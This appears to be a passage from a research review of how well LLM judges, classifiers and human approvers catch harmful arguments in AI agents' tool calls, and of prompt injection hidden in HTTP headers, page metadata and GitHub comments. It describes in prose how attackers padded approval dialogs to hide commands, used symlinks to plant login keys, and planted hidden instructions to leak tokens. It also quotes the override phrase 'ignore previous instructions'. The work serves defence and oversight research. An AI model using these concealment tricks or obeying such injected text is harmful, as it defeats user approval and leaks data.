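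The detector caught 36.8% of attacks that altered only arguments and 81.8% of those that altered only responses. Averaging alone can't explain this gap, because it divides both kinds of change by *n*. The argument changes must also have been smaller before averaging, as Zavrak suggests, or harder to tell from normal variation.

The 36.8% is based on only 57 argument-only attacks, so its 95% interval runs from about 26% to 50%. XGBoost, a simpler method, did better overall, with an AUROC of 0.975 and a recall of 92.7%. But only 7.2% of the attacks altered arguments alone, so XGBoost could have missed almost all of them and still reached that recall. Zavrak gives the breakdown by type of attack only for the graph network. The detectors may also have partly learned to recognise the style of one model, GLM-4-Flash, because it produced all the attacked sessions, while the normal ones came from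 eight models.

Format checks miss wrong arguments that are still valid, because the tool accepts them without an error. In *Measuring What Tool-Using LLM Agents Actually Do*, Gurram (2026) replaced one argument of an agent's first call with a wrong but valid value, such as Manchester instead of London for a weather tool, or a date 180 days off. One safeguard, which stopped a run at its second formatting or tool error, fired on 3.2% of 374 runs with a valid wrong argument and on 3.5% of runs of the same tasks without one.

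The swaps raised the share of wrong final answers by 22 percentage points, from 52.4% to 74.5%, over 1,085 pairs of runs. On the same pairs, a panel of three language-model judges registered an increase of only 2.5 points. This isn't good evidence that judges overlook arguments, because these judges weren't shown the calls. They compared each final answer with a reference text, and references such as "Weather analysis for Mumbai" contain no correct values.

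Gurram suggests comparing the executed arguments with the user's request. The city was swapped after the agent wrote its call, so a monitor that read only the agent's version would have seen the right city. Such a monitor would also have missed the bcc address that the postmark-mcp package added after the agent made its call.

### Strong judges that read the call

The results are much better when a strong model reads the actual call together with the user's request. Jia, Liu and colleagues (2026) tested this in *The Window Is in the Reasoning*, using agents that had read an injected instruction during simulated banking and workplace-chat tasks. The agents sometimes obeyed the instruction and sometimes ignored it. GPT-5 and Claude Opus 4.8 read the calls that followed and estimated the chance that they served an injected instruction, with an AUROC between 0.97 and 1.00. GPT-4o, given the same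 kind of input, couldn't tell calls that served the injected instruction from those the user had requested.

The researchers counted an agent as obeying if it made a call that changed something and contained an identifier belonging to the attacker, such as an account number, email address or URL. So a peripheral field was often what made the call harmful. But the judges also saw the tool output containing the injected instruction, so they could compare the calls with that instruction. Some of the planted tasks were also conspicuous, such as changing the account password when the user had asked about a bill. Noticing that would take less attention to detail than noticing one wrong recipient in an email the user had requested.

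An AUC near 1 also doesn't show how many false alarms a monitor would raise, because that depends on the threshold. In a related test, Jia and colleagues had judges read simulated next calls. On the chat tasks, the judges raised false alarms about agents that read every channel. The users had asked the agents to do this, but reading every channel was also the first step of the attack.

Judges that read only an agent's prose are much worse at detecting these faults. In one banking run, the agent changed a password as the attacker wanted, though its reasoning never mentioned a password. All six monitors that read the first half of the reasoning rated the risk near zero, while judges that read simulated next calls were nearly certain of an attack. In *Agentic Commerce Bench* (2026), a language-model judge that received only the agent's reasoning scored 0.05 when the agent's stated reason contradicted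 its payment request.

In *More Rejective, Not More Discriminative*, Han, Yan and Zhang (2026) set a harder test of argument checking. They took correct plans for a retail support agent and changed one action in each, using order and customer numbers from the simulated shop's database. The shop's software accepted every altered action, so no error message revealed the fault. Half of the 200 faults were wrong arguments in an action the customer had requested, such as exchanging an item for the wrong variant. The rest were actions on another customer's account or extra actions nobody had requested.

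Reviewing one action at a time, Claude Opus 4.8 rejected 98.5% of the faulty actions and 3.2% of the clean ones, a discrimination of 0.95. GPT-5.6 Sol reached 0.86. Qwen2.5-14B scored only 0.28, though it had scored 1.00 on all four unchanged-reply faults in *trajectory-judge*. The two tests differ in several ways, but the gap suggests that the earlier score was high in large part because the faults were easy and the prompt described them.

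Strong judges also had trouble in a second setting, where the agent worked across several apps. GPT-5.6 Sol rejected 99.5% of the actions with bad arguments but also 53% of the clean ones. Claude Opus 4.8 rejected 96.8% of the bad actions and 31% of the clean ones, so both models would have blocked a lot of legitimate work. The retail false-alarm rates are less certain because they move in steps of about 1/31, which implies only around 31 distinct clean cases. One more rejection would add about three percentage points.

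### Length and position

Han and colleagues designed their test mainly to find out how many planned actions a judge should review at once. The faulty action always came last, and they varied how many of the preceding actions were in the batch. The table shows each judge's discrimination in the retail setting.

| Judge | 1 action | 2 | 3 | 5 | 8 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 0.95 | 0.81 | 0.68 | 0.26 | 0.00 |
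| GPT-5.6 Sol | 0.86 | 0.71 | 0.44 | 0.09 | 0.00 |
| DeepSeek-V4-Pro | 0.78 | 0.67 | 0.34 | 0.10 | −0.01 |
| Qwen2.5-72B | 0.67 | 0.50 | 0.37 | 0.06 | 0.00 |
| Llama-3.3-70B | 0.35 | 0.60 | 0.35 | 0.11 | 0.04 |
| Qwen2.5-14B | 0.28 | 0.42 | 0.21 | 0.01 | 0.00 |

At eight actions the judges rejected almost everything, clean or faulty. Recall alone would have made the longest batches look best.

The main cause of the low scores on large batches seems to be missing information, rather than long records overwhelming the judge. The actions in a batch haven't run yet, so the judge doesn't have their results. Without the result of an order lookup, for example, it can't tell whether an order number is right. Larger batches hide more results, and in this test they also made the prompt shorter. When the researchers restored the hidden results for Llama-3.3-70B, its score at eight actions rose from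 0.04 to 0.49, which is higher than its score on single actions.

*StepShield* (2026), a test of how early monitors catch rogue agents, compared runs of different lengths. A language-model judge's early-intervention rate was 0.71 on runs of 3 to 8 steps and 0.47 on runs of 15 to 20. Three other detectors each lost a larger share of their performance than the judge did. The longer runs may have contained harder cases. A second comparison used the same runs but varied how much history the judge received. The judge's recall was 58% with the current step alone, 62% with the five preceding steps and 60% with the full history. Without false-alarm rates, these small differences could partly reflect a change in how readily the judge flags anything.

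Caldwell and colleagues found that earlier calls lowered recall for most of their judges, but this result is similarly ambiguous because false alarms often fell as well. Length probably does some harm, but none of these tests fully separates its effect from those of missing results, harder tasks or a more cautious judge. The runs are also short. A complete run in *trajectory-judge* has six steps, while current agents can work for hours.

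The effect of a detail's position is harder to isolate. Han and colleagues' main comparison keeps the fault in the last slot, and in *trajectory-judge* each type of fault has its own fixed step, so position and type change together. The well-known position bias in language-model judges concerns the order in which two competing answers appear, so it doesn't show whether a judge is more likely to overlook a bad recipient in the middle of a record than at the end.

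### The same harm in different fields

The most direct test of the hypothesis would put the same harm in different fields and compare how well the monitor distinguishes harmful actions from harmless ones in each case. For example, an agent could send the same salary table to the same outsider through the "to" line, the bcc line or the query string of a URL. A search of work from 2025 and 2026 found no such test.

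Existing tests tend to change the field and the harm together. In *trajectory-judge*, a wrong amount costs the shop money, while an invented product code only causes a failed lookup. Mou and colleagues treat benign tools with risky arguments as a separate category, but report their main results by source dataset rather than by category. Sinha (2026), in *Exposure Is Not Commitment*, finds that a simple policy on tools trivially catches an unsafe call once it is visible, but scores only attacks that make the agent choose an unsafe tool, not those that change an argument of a tool the task requires.

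Xu comes closest, with a test that moves a leak from one part of a response to another. To detect leaks of another customer's data, the monitors compared two runs of the same request in which only that data differed. When they compared only the field the user had asked about, they caught 99.7% of leaks in that field and 1.4% of leaks elsewhere, and flagged 0.9% of clean cases. The instructions created this very large blind spot by limiting the comparison to one field.

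Comparing the whole response caught 90.4% of the leaks elsewhere and flagged 75.7% of clean cases, because the wording of a response varies from run to run anyway. Discrimination was therefore only about 0.15. Xu derives a condition for when it pays to compare one more field. Let *P* be the share of leaks that occur in the fields already compared, *p* the share that occur in the new field, and *q* the chance that the new field differs between two clean runs. Assuming that fields vary independently, adding the field improves accuracy only if:

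```
p × (1 − q) / q > P
```

If the existing fields carry 90% of leaks and the new one carries 5%, *q* must be below about 5.3%. A recipient address or file path could plausibly meet that condition, since it should seldom change when the request stays the same, but the free text of an email almost never would.

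## What people notice when they approve an agent's actions

Many agents ask their user to approve an action before it runs, as Claude Code did by default until August 2026. The prompt usually shows the pending command or call, and the user clicks to approve or reject it. A harmful argument can get past this check if the screen doesn't show it, if the user doesn't read it, or if the user reads it without understanding what it does.

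### One dangerous command in a coding session

In the largest test of human approval, Anthropic hired 1,053 testers through a research vendor for a coding study. The testers knew they were being evaluated, but not on what. Partway through each session, the researchers replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command, and the vendor recorded whether the tester approved it. Approving it never ran anything dangerous.

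The testers rejected 143 of the commands (13.6%). Auto mode's classifier blocked 937 of the same commands (89%). Anthropic also reports that the classifier blocked 800 commands that testers approved, while testers rejected 6 that the classifier allowed. The other cells follow by subtraction:

| | Classifier blocked | Classifier allowed | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tester rejected | 137 | 6 | 143 |
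| Tester approved | 800 | 110 | 910 |
| Total | 937 | 116 | 1,053 |

As Willison pointed out, the classifier still let 11% of the commands through. The testers rejected only 6 of these 116 commands, so the two checks together would have stopped 943 commands, or 89.6%, compared with 89.0% for the classifier alone. If the testers' rejections had been unrelated to the classifier's, they would have caught about 16 of the 116, so the commands that the classifier missed were probably harder for people too.

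Testers caught the dangerous command about 17% of the time early in a session and about 5% of the time after 50 or more prompts, while the classifier's detection rate stayed flat. Each tester saw only one dangerous command, so the early and late rates come from different testers. Those who had clicked through 50 prompts may have been hastier from the start.

Anthropic was evaluating its own product, and it published the results when it announced that auto mode would become the default. The testers weren't working on their own code, so they had nothing to lose if a file was deleted. Developers with more at stake might check more carefully. But a command that an agent really proposed would probably fit the task better than a swapped-in one, so it could be harder to notice.

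The study also reports no false-alarm rate for the testers. Claude Code's users reject about 3% of permission requests in normal use. If the testers rejected ordinary requests at the same rate, they flagged dangerous commands about 11 percentage points more often than ordinary ones, and only about 2 points more often late in a session. This estimate is rough because the two groups differ.

In Anthropic's data from real use, among sessions that its safety pipeline had flagged, 6.3% of the manually approved ones contained a seriously harmful action that the user hadn't explicitly requested, compared with 2.4% of those in auto mode. This comparison is limited because a model graded the harm and people who choose auto mode may do different work.

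### Plans and single commands

Claude Code users reject 39% of the plans the agent presents, but only 3% of individual permission requests. Plans are mostly prose and permission requests are mostly commands, so this is consistent with people scrutinising prose more closely than commands.

The difference in rejection rates between plans and commands doesn't prove that people review commands less carefully. Users who like most of a plan may reject it just to ask for a change. Most commands are safe, and if only 3% were bad, a perfect reviewer would reject 3%. Users also see dozens or hundreds of permission requests a day, which makes fatigue more likely. Plans also give users more information. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) finds that plans are among the most informative things agents ask people to approve, whereas most prompts in current products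 show a raw command on a single line.

Rejection rates can't separate these explanations, because nobody knows how many of the plans or commands should have been rejected. Approval also doesn't always reflect a judgement about the command. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of software practitioners, suggests that repeated approval may come from habit, fatigue or a need to keep work moving rather than from growing trust. Some commands also run without a prompt. In June 2026, 49.5% of Claude Code's active command-line users had written a rule that allows this for some shell commands, and a quarter of interactive sessions started in a mode that skips permission prompts.

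### Arguments missing from the screen

Even a careful reviewer can't notice a command argument that the approval dialog doesn't show. In 2025, the code editor Cursor had a dialog for installing MCP servers from a link that left out the arguments of the command it was about to run, according to *CVE-2025-54133* in the US government's National Vulnerability Database (NVD). A user could see a familiar program name and unknowingly approve an attacker's instructions to that program. Cursor fixed the flaw in version 1.3 by showing the arguments.

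That fix was incomplete. In *The Cursor deeplink vulnerability*, Utevsky (2026) found that the dialog put the arguments in a single-line box. Utevsky entered `calc`, the name of the Windows calculator, followed by a long run of tabs and then a command that contacted an attacker's server. The dialog showed only `calc` because the rest was beyond the right edge of the box. Cursor's staff had identified the cause and traced it to a report from 27 April 2026, but the attack still worked on the latest version on 15 July.

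The personal assistant OpenClaw had a similar problem twice. According to NVD's *CVE-2026-26320*, when a link triggered its Mac app to run a message, the confirmation dialog showed only the first 240 characters but the app ran the whole message. An attacker could use blank space to push the harmful part out of the preview. OpenClaw fixed this in February 2026. GitLab's *GHSA-xww8-gqvh-92x9* (2026) describes the second case, in which the approval screen for shell commands shortened very long commands but OpenClaw ran them in full. Since version 2026.5.18, OpenClaw has rejected commands that are too long to display, according to SecureLayer7's *CVE-2026-53829*. This is safer than lengthening the preview, because an attacker could still hide the harmful part by adding more padding.

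Google's Gemini CLI, another coding agent, could be made to run hidden commands without asking the user for approval. In June 2025 the security company Tracebit reported that an attacker could add commands that steal data after a `grep` text search, using blank space to hide them. Gemini CLI treated the whole line as a search and ran it without a prompt. Google's fix, released that July, shows the commands and asks for explicit approval of suspicious ones, according to ITPro's *A flaw in Google’s new Gemini CLI tool*.

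An approval screen can also show an argument in full without showing its effect. *GhostApproval* (2026), by the security company Wiz, describes an attack that uses symbolic links, which are files that redirect to other files. Wiz made a project in which `project_settings.json` redirected to the list of keys that can log in to the user's computer, and included instructions for the agent to add the attacker's key to the "settings". Cursor and Google's Antigravity showed the harmless filename and, after approval, wrote to the real target. In a test of Claude Code, the agent noted in its reasoning that the file was a shell configuration file, but Claude Code asked the user only whether to edit `project_settings.json`.

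Cursor, Google and Amazon fixed the problem. Augment and Windsurf acknowledged the reports but had announced no fix by July 2026. In Amazon's and Windsurf's assistants, the agent wrote to the file before the user could respond, so a clearer prompt wouldn't have prevented the change.

Anthropic rejected Wiz's report as outside its threat model because the user had trusted the folder and approved the edit. Claude Code now warns about such links. Anthropic says the warning shipped in version 2.1.32 on 5 February 2026, nine days before Wiz reported the problem, but Wiz lists the later version 2.1.42 as affected.

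It also matters who writes the text the approver reads. Kodathala, Pollishetty and Cargill (2026), in *Approve What, Exactly?*, tested an email much like the one with the planted bcc address. The user had asked the agent to send a report to their boss, and the compromised agent added a blind copy to an attacker. Fifteen language models acted as approvers. All 15 approved the email when they read the agent's own description, which left out the blind copy, and all 15 refused it when they read a card that separate software had built from the actual call.

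This shows that the card contained enough information for a correct decision, but not that people would use it. Across all the attacks in this test, the models caught 30% without the card and 98% with it. The models also refused 16% of harmless requests designed to resemble attacks, mostly because of a flaw in the test material.

An approval screen that shows the call correctly doesn't help if the call changes after the user approves it. Kodathala and colleagues could test eight approval mechanisms for this problem, and four let someone change the arguments after approval.

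### Arguments on the screen that people overlook

In *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026) tested how much it helps people to see the arguments. They showed each of 80 volunteers one of four approval screens and had them judge 12 requests from an agent, half of them harmful.

| Screen | Harmful requests approved | Harmless requests approved | Median time |
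|---|---|---|---|
| Short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
| + exact arguments | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| + user's limits and full log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
| Same facts, with the consequence stated | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

Adding the arguments reduced approvals of harmful actions by about 12 percentage points and had little effect on approvals of harmless ones. The reduction is uncertain because only 20 people saw each screen. Even treating every decision as independent, which overstates the precision, gives a 95% interval from an increase of about 1 point to a reduction of 24.

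Two thirds of the harmful requests looked fine on their own and broke the user's limits only because of earlier steps. For example, an attachment might be permitted but contain forbidden data that the agent used in an earlier step. In the other third, the problem was in the call itself. People who had the arguments, the user's limits and the full log still approved 10 of those 40 requests. So people sometimes miss faults in arguments they can see, but the study has no comparable figure for faults in prose.

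These volunteers still did much better than Anthropic's testers. The volunteers' only task was to review requests, half of which were harmful. This suggests that people miss dangerous commands in normal work partly because they aren't looking for them, not only because they can't recognise them.

Research on phishing, where a fake website imitates a real one, provides an older baseline. The web address is a peripheral field that often reveals the fake. In *Why Phishing Works* (2006), Dhamija, Tygar and Hearst asked 22 people to judge whether 20 websites were genuine. 23% of participants didn't look at the address bar or other browser cues, and they judged 40% of the sites wrongly. The most convincing fake copied a bank's site at bankofthevvest.com, with two v's in place of the w. It fooled about 90% of participants, including people who did look at browser cues.

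Alsharnouby, Alaca and Chiasson tracked the eye movements of 21 people in *Why Phishing Still Works* (2015). The participants knew they were looking for phishing sites but detected only 53% of them. They spent very little time looking at the browser's security indicators compared with the page itself, and those who looked longer at the browser's own elements tended to detect more phishing sites. General technical skill made no clear difference. The sample was small and browsers have changed since, but the results fit the idea that people judge mostly by the main content.

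People can also miss problems in the main content. In *Are You Sure?*, Li, Dai and colleagues (2026) had 303 people work with compromised agents on realistic tasks, without telling them to expect an attack. In one task, a hidden note in a résumé biased the agent helping to choose a job candidate. Only 8.6% of participants noticed an attack. In tasks like this one, the deception reaches the user through the agent's ordinary advice, so the low figure isn't evidence of a blind spot specific to an action's arguments.

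### Commands that people read but don't understand

Even a careful reader can learn little from some commands. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) found that uninformative approval prompts contributed to 31 of 290 reports of problems with agents and files. One example is `python3 setup.py`, which looks routine but runs whatever code is in the script. Showing the full command doesn't help here, as with the `./tool` command that overwrote a source file.

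Anthropic's testers had a clearly dangerous command in the prompt, so a missing field can't explain most of their misses. Their knowledge of commands presumably didn't decline during a session, so the fall from 17% to 5% is better explained by testers not reading the prompt than by their not understanding it. The low rate at the start is harder to explain, and Anthropic reports no measure of what the testers looked at or understood.

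Hossain and colleagues did test understanding. People answered 57.1% of the comprehension questions correctly with the short description, 67.9% with the arguments and 76.7% with the full log. The fourth screen added a sentence on what the action would do, for example that the attachment was built from raw invoice rows and would go to the auditor, and with it people answered 81.7% correctly.

That screen reduced harmful approvals by 7.9 percentage points compared with the log, after statistical adjustment, but the 95% interval runs from a reduction of 19.7 points to an increase of 3.8. It made no difference when the harm depended on a chain of several steps, where people approved 7 of 30 harmful requests with either screen. Hossain and colleagues also didn't test what happens when the stated consequence is wrong. People who rely on it might check the arguments less carefully than they would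 without it.

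## Instructions to AI in web headers and page metadata

When an agent opens a web page, it may receive text that a person viewing the page never sees, and the site's operator can use that text to give the agent instructions. Researchers who searched the web for such instructions in 2025 and 2026 found them on a tiny share of sites, often in HTTP headers. Most were pranks, protests or attempts to disrupt scraping, and few aimed at theft.

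### From a web response to a model's input

An agent usually opens a page through a fetch tool, which requests the URL and turns some of the response into text for the model. The invented response below has an instruction in six places, each marked with a bracketed label.

```
HTTP/1.1 200 OK
Content-Type: text/html
X-AI: [instruction in a header]

<html>
<head>
  <title>Opening hours</title>
  <meta name="llm-directive" content="[instruction in a meta tag]">
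  <script type="application/ld+json">
    {"@type": "Store", "description": "[instruction in structured data]"}
  </script>
</head>
<body>
  <!-- [instruction in a comment] -->
  <p>We are open from 9 to 5.</p>
  <p style="display:none">[instruction in a hidden element]</p>
  <p style="color:white">[instruction in white text]</p>
</body>
</html>
```

On a white background, a person sees only the opening hours. Meta tags hold information about the page, such as the text for a link preview, and structured data gives search engines a machine-readable summary.

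*Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* (Khodayari, Acharya, Zhang and Pellegrino, 2026), the largest study of such instructions, tested four ways of presenting a page to a model. Plain text is the body with its HTML tags removed, and HTML is the body with its markup. The raw response adds the headers. A page snapshot is a text outline of the page after a browser has rendered it. The table shows which of the six instructions would normally reach the model, though tools and settings vary.

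| Place | Plain text | HTML | Raw response | Snapshot |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Header | No | No | Yes | No |
| Meta tag | No | Yes | Yes | No |
| Structured data | Usually not | Yes | Yes | No |
| Comment | No | Yes | Yes | No |
| Hidden element | Yes | Yes | Yes | Usually not |
| White text | Yes | Yes | Yes | Usually |

Converting the page to plain text keeps the hidden paragraph but removes the style setting that hid it. The model would read "We are open from 9 to 5" followed by two instructions, with no sign that visitors can't see them.

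Other tools convert pages differently. The method in *Decoding Latent Attack Surfaces in LLMs* (2025) loads each page in a browser, extracts the full HTML and the visible text, and gives both to the models. The pipeline in *An Index-based Approach for Efficient and Effective Web Content Extraction* (2025) deletes HTML comments, scripts and styling before it converts the page to Markdown. *Hidden-in-Plain-Text* (2026) includes an optional cleaning step that neutralises hidden and off-screen text but keeps visible text. Extraction can also lose visible text. In a simulation in *Pretraining Data Can Be Poisoned through Computational Propaganda* (2026), 71.9% of the comments planted in pages' visible comment sections survived conversion to plain text.

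### What a search of 1.2 billion URLs found

Khodayari and colleagues searched about half of the October 2025 edition of Common Crawl, a public archive of web pages, for 3,963 phrases typical of prompt injection, such as "ignore previous instructions" and its variants. The half they searched covered 1.2 billion URLs on 24.8 million hosts (site addresses such as www.example.com). They also searched for known phrases in Censys and Shodan, two services that scan the internet for servers. In total, they confirmed 15,387 instructions on 11,722 pages.

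| Place | Instructions | Share |
|---|---|---|
| HTTP headers | 7,887 | 51.3% |
| HTML elements, such as paragraphs | 4,608 | 29.9% |
| Structured data | 1,996 | 13.0% |
| Comments | 675 | 4.4% |
| Meta tags and page titles | 221 | 1.4% |

About 70% of the instructions were therefore in places that a browser doesn't display as part of the page. The rest were in HTML elements, which a browser normally displays, so the researchers loaded those pages in January 2026 to check whether a visitor could see the instructions. Many were gone by then. Of the 2,939 whose visibility they could still check, 92% were hidden, for example by tiny type, text the same colour as its background, or another element on top.

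The most common instruction, which appeared 3,504 times, told the model to ignore its previous instructions and return random numbers. The researchers classed 8,894 instructions as attempts to disrupt AI systems, 4,093 as attempts to restrict the use of content, and 3,096 as ways to detect bots, with some instructions in more than one category. Only 13 tried to extract secrets or a system prompt. The study doesn't break these purposes down by where the instructions appeared, so we can't tell from it whether instructions in headers are more or less hostile than others.

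The instructions are also not independent of one another. One template, which tells the model to repeat a fixed string indefinitely, appeared on 1,018 of the 2,042 affected hosts, and a header called X-LLM appeared on 1,017. These nearly equal counts suggest that most of those hosts sent the same header, perhaps because they had the same operator or software.

### How the search method affects the figures

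The keyword search could find only instructions that resembled its keywords, so it missed those that were in other languages, disguised or worded in unfamiliar ways. Many of the search phrases described overriding the model's task, which partly explains why 99% of the confirmed instructions tried to do this.

Prompt injections in headers are more likely to be overcounted than those in page bodies. A matching phrase in a page's body may come from a tutorial or news story about prompt injection, so two reviewers checked those matches in context, often in groups. They accepted every header match without individual review, reasoning that such a phrase is very unlikely to be in a header by accident. This shortcut is reasonable, but trackr.live's *Half the Validated Prompt Injections Rode in HTTP Headers* (2026) points out that test servers and copied configurations could also contain these phrases.

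Counting header matches automatically affects a large part of the total. At least 5,408 of the 27,860 matches in Common Crawl were in headers. If no others were, the reviewers confirmed only about 30% of the non-header matches.

Including Censys and Shodan raised the share of instructions found in headers. The study attributes 5,408 header instructions in Common Crawl to site operators, which is probably all of them, since operators control their own headers. If so, headers would account for about 45% of the 12,075 instructions found in Common Crawl and about 75% of the 3,312 from the other two services. "Just over half" therefore describes this mix of sources and is not an estimate for the web as a whole.

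### How rare the instructions are

Only the Common Crawl results can give a prevalence, because the researchers know how many pages and hosts they searched there:

```
hosts:      285 / 24,834,442    ≈ 0.00115%, about 1 in 87,000
pages:    9,676 / 1.2 billion   ≈ 0.0008%,  about 1 in 124,000
```

Dividing all 2,042 affected hosts by 24.8 million would give about 1 in 12,000, which is seven times too high because most of those hosts came from the targeted searches and weren't among the 24.8 million.

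At the page rate above, an agent that fetched 20,000 random pages a day would encounter one of these instructions about every six days. Real agents don't browse at random. The instructions were rarer on the 10,000 most popular domains, but job listings, shopping and some other types of site had higher rates even among popular domains. An agent that applies for jobs could therefore encounter them more often than one that reads the news.

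The true rate could also be higher because Common Crawl would miss any instruction that a server sends only to visitors it identifies as agents. It also misses most pages behind a login, including much of social media.

### How often models obeyed

Khodayari and colleagues then tested 100 distinct instructions from their collection on 13 models, including GPT-5.4 and several small open models. For each instruction, every model had to summarise a page containing it in each of the four representations, which made 1,300 runs per representation. The researchers checked every output by hand. The last column below is calculated from the published rates.

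| Representation | Obeyed | Failed with an error | Obeyed, among runs without an error |
|---|---|---|---|
| Plain text | 3.9% | 0.7% | 4.0% |
| HTML | 1.1% | 20.3% | 1.4% |
| Page snapshot | 1.1% | 3.5% | 1.1% |
| Raw response | 0.2% | 25.8% | 0.2% |

The raw response had the lowest compliance rate, but about a quarter of its runs failed because the input was longer than the model could accept. The low rate therefore doesn't show that the format is safe, since a model that accepts longer inputs might obey the instruction. Excluding the failed runs doesn't fully correct for this, because small models obeyed most often and were also the most sensitive to long inputs. The remaining runs probably over-represent models that rarely obey.

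Converting pages to plain text has the opposite problem, because it removes headers and comments. The study doesn't report how many of the 100 instructions survived each conversion. If some were in headers, the plain-text version left them out, and the models' compliance rate for the instructions they did receive would be above 3.9%.

The researchers attribute the high plain-text rate to clues in the other formats that an instruction is hidden. HTML markup shows that the instruction is inside a comment or styled to be invisible, whereas in plain text it looks like part of the article. Small models followed the plain-text instructions 8% of the time.

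Failed runs explain at most part of the difference between plain text and HTML. The published totals imply that the medium-sized and closed models followed the instructions in 17 of 700 plain-text runs and in none of 700 HTML runs. These models had 315 errors across all four formats, so at least 385 of their HTML runs finished. At the plain-text rate, the models would have followed the instructions in about nine of those.

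That still doesn't prove that the clues made the difference. HTML pages are much longer, so the instruction is a smaller part of the input. A snapshot can also leave out a hidden element that plain text keeps, so the model never receives the instruction. To separate these effects, a test would have to keep the length and the instruction constant and remove only the styling that shows the instruction is hidden.

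Structure can help with other kinds of detection too. *MemoPhishAgent* (2026), a system that uses a language model to detect phishing pages, performed about equally well on HTML and Markdown but lost a few percentage points of recall on plain text, probably because the plain text lacked cues such as headings and links.

All these compliance rates come from a single request for a summary. The models had no tools, so the test doesn't show whether an instruction that changed a summary would also make an agent send an email or run a command.

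### Headers a year later

In October 2026, Signals Corps published *Prompt injection in HTTP headers* (Andrews, 2026). The company sells security software for AI agents, so it has a commercial interest in the subject. Andrews searched only the headers of 217 million responses, a tenth of Common Crawl's September 2026 edition, for any text written for AI systems.

Andrews found such headers on 7,959 sites. On 7,271 of them, the header pointed agents to another resource, usually a file called `llms.txt`, which describes a site for language models. Only 30 sites sent what Andrews classed as an injection attempt, and 22 of those were pranks. A few of the other eight sent instructions to take real actions, which would work only if the agent had the necessary capability, such as shell or database access.

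The two searches found these headers at roughly similar rates. Andrews found about one site with an injection attempt per 7 million responses. Khodayari and colleagues found instructions from site operators, including those in headers, on 179 hosts in Common Crawl data, or about one host per 7 million URLs. The comparison is crude because some sites have far more pages than others and the two teams defined an injection differently.

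The pointers are a more common way to reach an agent than the injection attempts. An agent that follows a pointer fetches a second page, which could contain its own instructions, so Andrews recommends treating that page as untrusted. The scan also found 136 sites whose headers showed that they had classified Common Crawl's crawler as an AI bot. A server that can classify visitors this way can also send agents different content than it sends people.

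Signals Corps also ran a small test with three Claude models (Opus, Sonnet and Haiku) in Claude Code. Ordinary tasks, such as checking whether a site was up, brought the headers into the model's input. The models noticed the test instructions and didn't follow them by default, but they obeyed in seven of the nine runs in which the user had asked them to follow any instructions from the site.

Those seven runs are weak evidence that headers can hijack an agent, because the user had told the model to do what the site asked. But they do show that a broad instruction from the user can give authority to text the user has never seen. Nine runs are also too few to estimate a reliable rate. The company's commercial interest is a reason to be careful with its advice, but its main finding, that injection attempts in headers are rare and mostly pranks, doesn't obviously help it sell software.

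### Text and metadata inside the page

Google searched the text of pages in several editions of Common Crawl and published the results in April 2026. It looked for known phrases, had its Gemini model judge the intent of each match and whether the text was out of place, and then had people review the results. Most of the initial matches were harmless material about prompt injection. The genuine instructions included pranks, requests to add context to summaries, and attempts to promote a business or keep AI agents away. One site tried to lure agents to a page that never finished loading.

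Google saw few attempts to steal data and no significant number of advanced attacks like those researchers had published. Its malicious category grew by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026, but Google gives no counts, so this rise could represent a handful of pages or thousands. The search covered text inside pages, so it doesn't show whether instructions in headers became more common.

Some hidden instructions are meant to make AI agents send money. Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild* describes two found by the security company Forcepoint. One gave complete instructions for a PayPal payment, and the other used a meta tag to steer agents to a donation link. Mascellino (2026), in *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents*, reports that another security company, Zscaler, found sites with hidden text meant to get agents to make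 cryptocurrency payments. These findings show that some site owners intend fraud, but Forcepoint's don't establish that any agent paid.

### Comments that only the agent receives

GitHub, a site where programmers share code, doesn't display HTML comments on its web pages, but most AI agents receive the raw text, which includes them. A project's agents can therefore read text in a bug report that its maintainers don't see. In *Who Is Prompt-Injecting Coding Agents?*, Nakibly and Babo (2026) searched 142.7 million bug reports, proposed changes and comments for hidden text addressed to AI.

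Of the 2,281 confirmed cases, 43 were attacks. One attack, from July 2026, was in a bug report for Google's Gemini CLI. A maintainer reading the report on the website would have seen only a description of a crash. A hidden comment told the project's agent for finding duplicate reports to copy a secret access token to a place where a later step might expose it.

Nakibly and Babo replayed the 43 attacks offline against five models. One small, fast model carried out 19% of them. When they removed the HTML comments from the input, no model carried out any of the attacks. This is stronger evidence for removing a field than Khodayari and colleagues' comparison of formats, because Nakibly and Babo tested the same attacks with and without the comments.

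However, removing comments would also remove the notes that projects leave for their own agents, for example to mark a task as taken. Such notes made up two thirds of the cases. Headers are easier to leave out, since most tasks need only a few of them. trackr.live recommends that fetch tools omit headers by default and pass on only the values the agent needs, labelled with their source.

### Detection rates that don't measure monitors

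Khodayari and colleagues also found that closed models flagged the injection in their summaries in 25.1% of runs, and small models in 4.8%. In six cases, a model identified the instruction but still followed it.

The models were asked to summarise the page, not to look for hidden instructions, so these rates don't measure a monitor's recall. Xu's test with leaked personal details showed that a model can recognise many more faults when its prompt tells it to check for them. Some runs of the summarisation test failed, and in others the conversion may have removed the instruction. The test also had no clean pages, so it gives no false-alarm rate.

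The searches suggest that simple rules would raise many false alarms. A rule that looked for AI-related words in header names would have flagged 910 sites in Andrews' scan whose headers weren't written for AI. Of the 7,959 sites whose headers were written for AI, only 0.4% had sent an injection attempt. Nakibly and Babo searched a month of GitHub text for keywords, and 116 of the 123 matches left after initial filtering were false alarms, mostly ordinary English or people discussing prompt injection.

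These studies measure how often hostile text appears in headers and metadata and whether it can reach a model. None compared how a monitor handles an agent's record when the instruction is in a header with how it handles the same record when the instruction is in the visible page or absent. Many monitors couldn't be tested this way without modification. Claude Code's classifier, for example, doesn't receive the pages an agent fetches, so it can catch a successful injection only through the calls the agent makes afterward.

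## Incidents involving titles, filenames and URLs

Attackers and security researchers have used issue titles, filenames, tool descriptions and URLs to make AI agents install software, leak data or give false advice. Six cases from 2025 and 2026 are documented well enough to ask whether a monitor was running and whether it received the relevant field. The Cline, Datadog and Deadbugz cases were attacks on real software projects, though only the Cline attack reached ordinary users. EchoLeak, Rovo and HashJack were demonstrations by researchers, with no reported victims.

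### An issue title that led to an altered release

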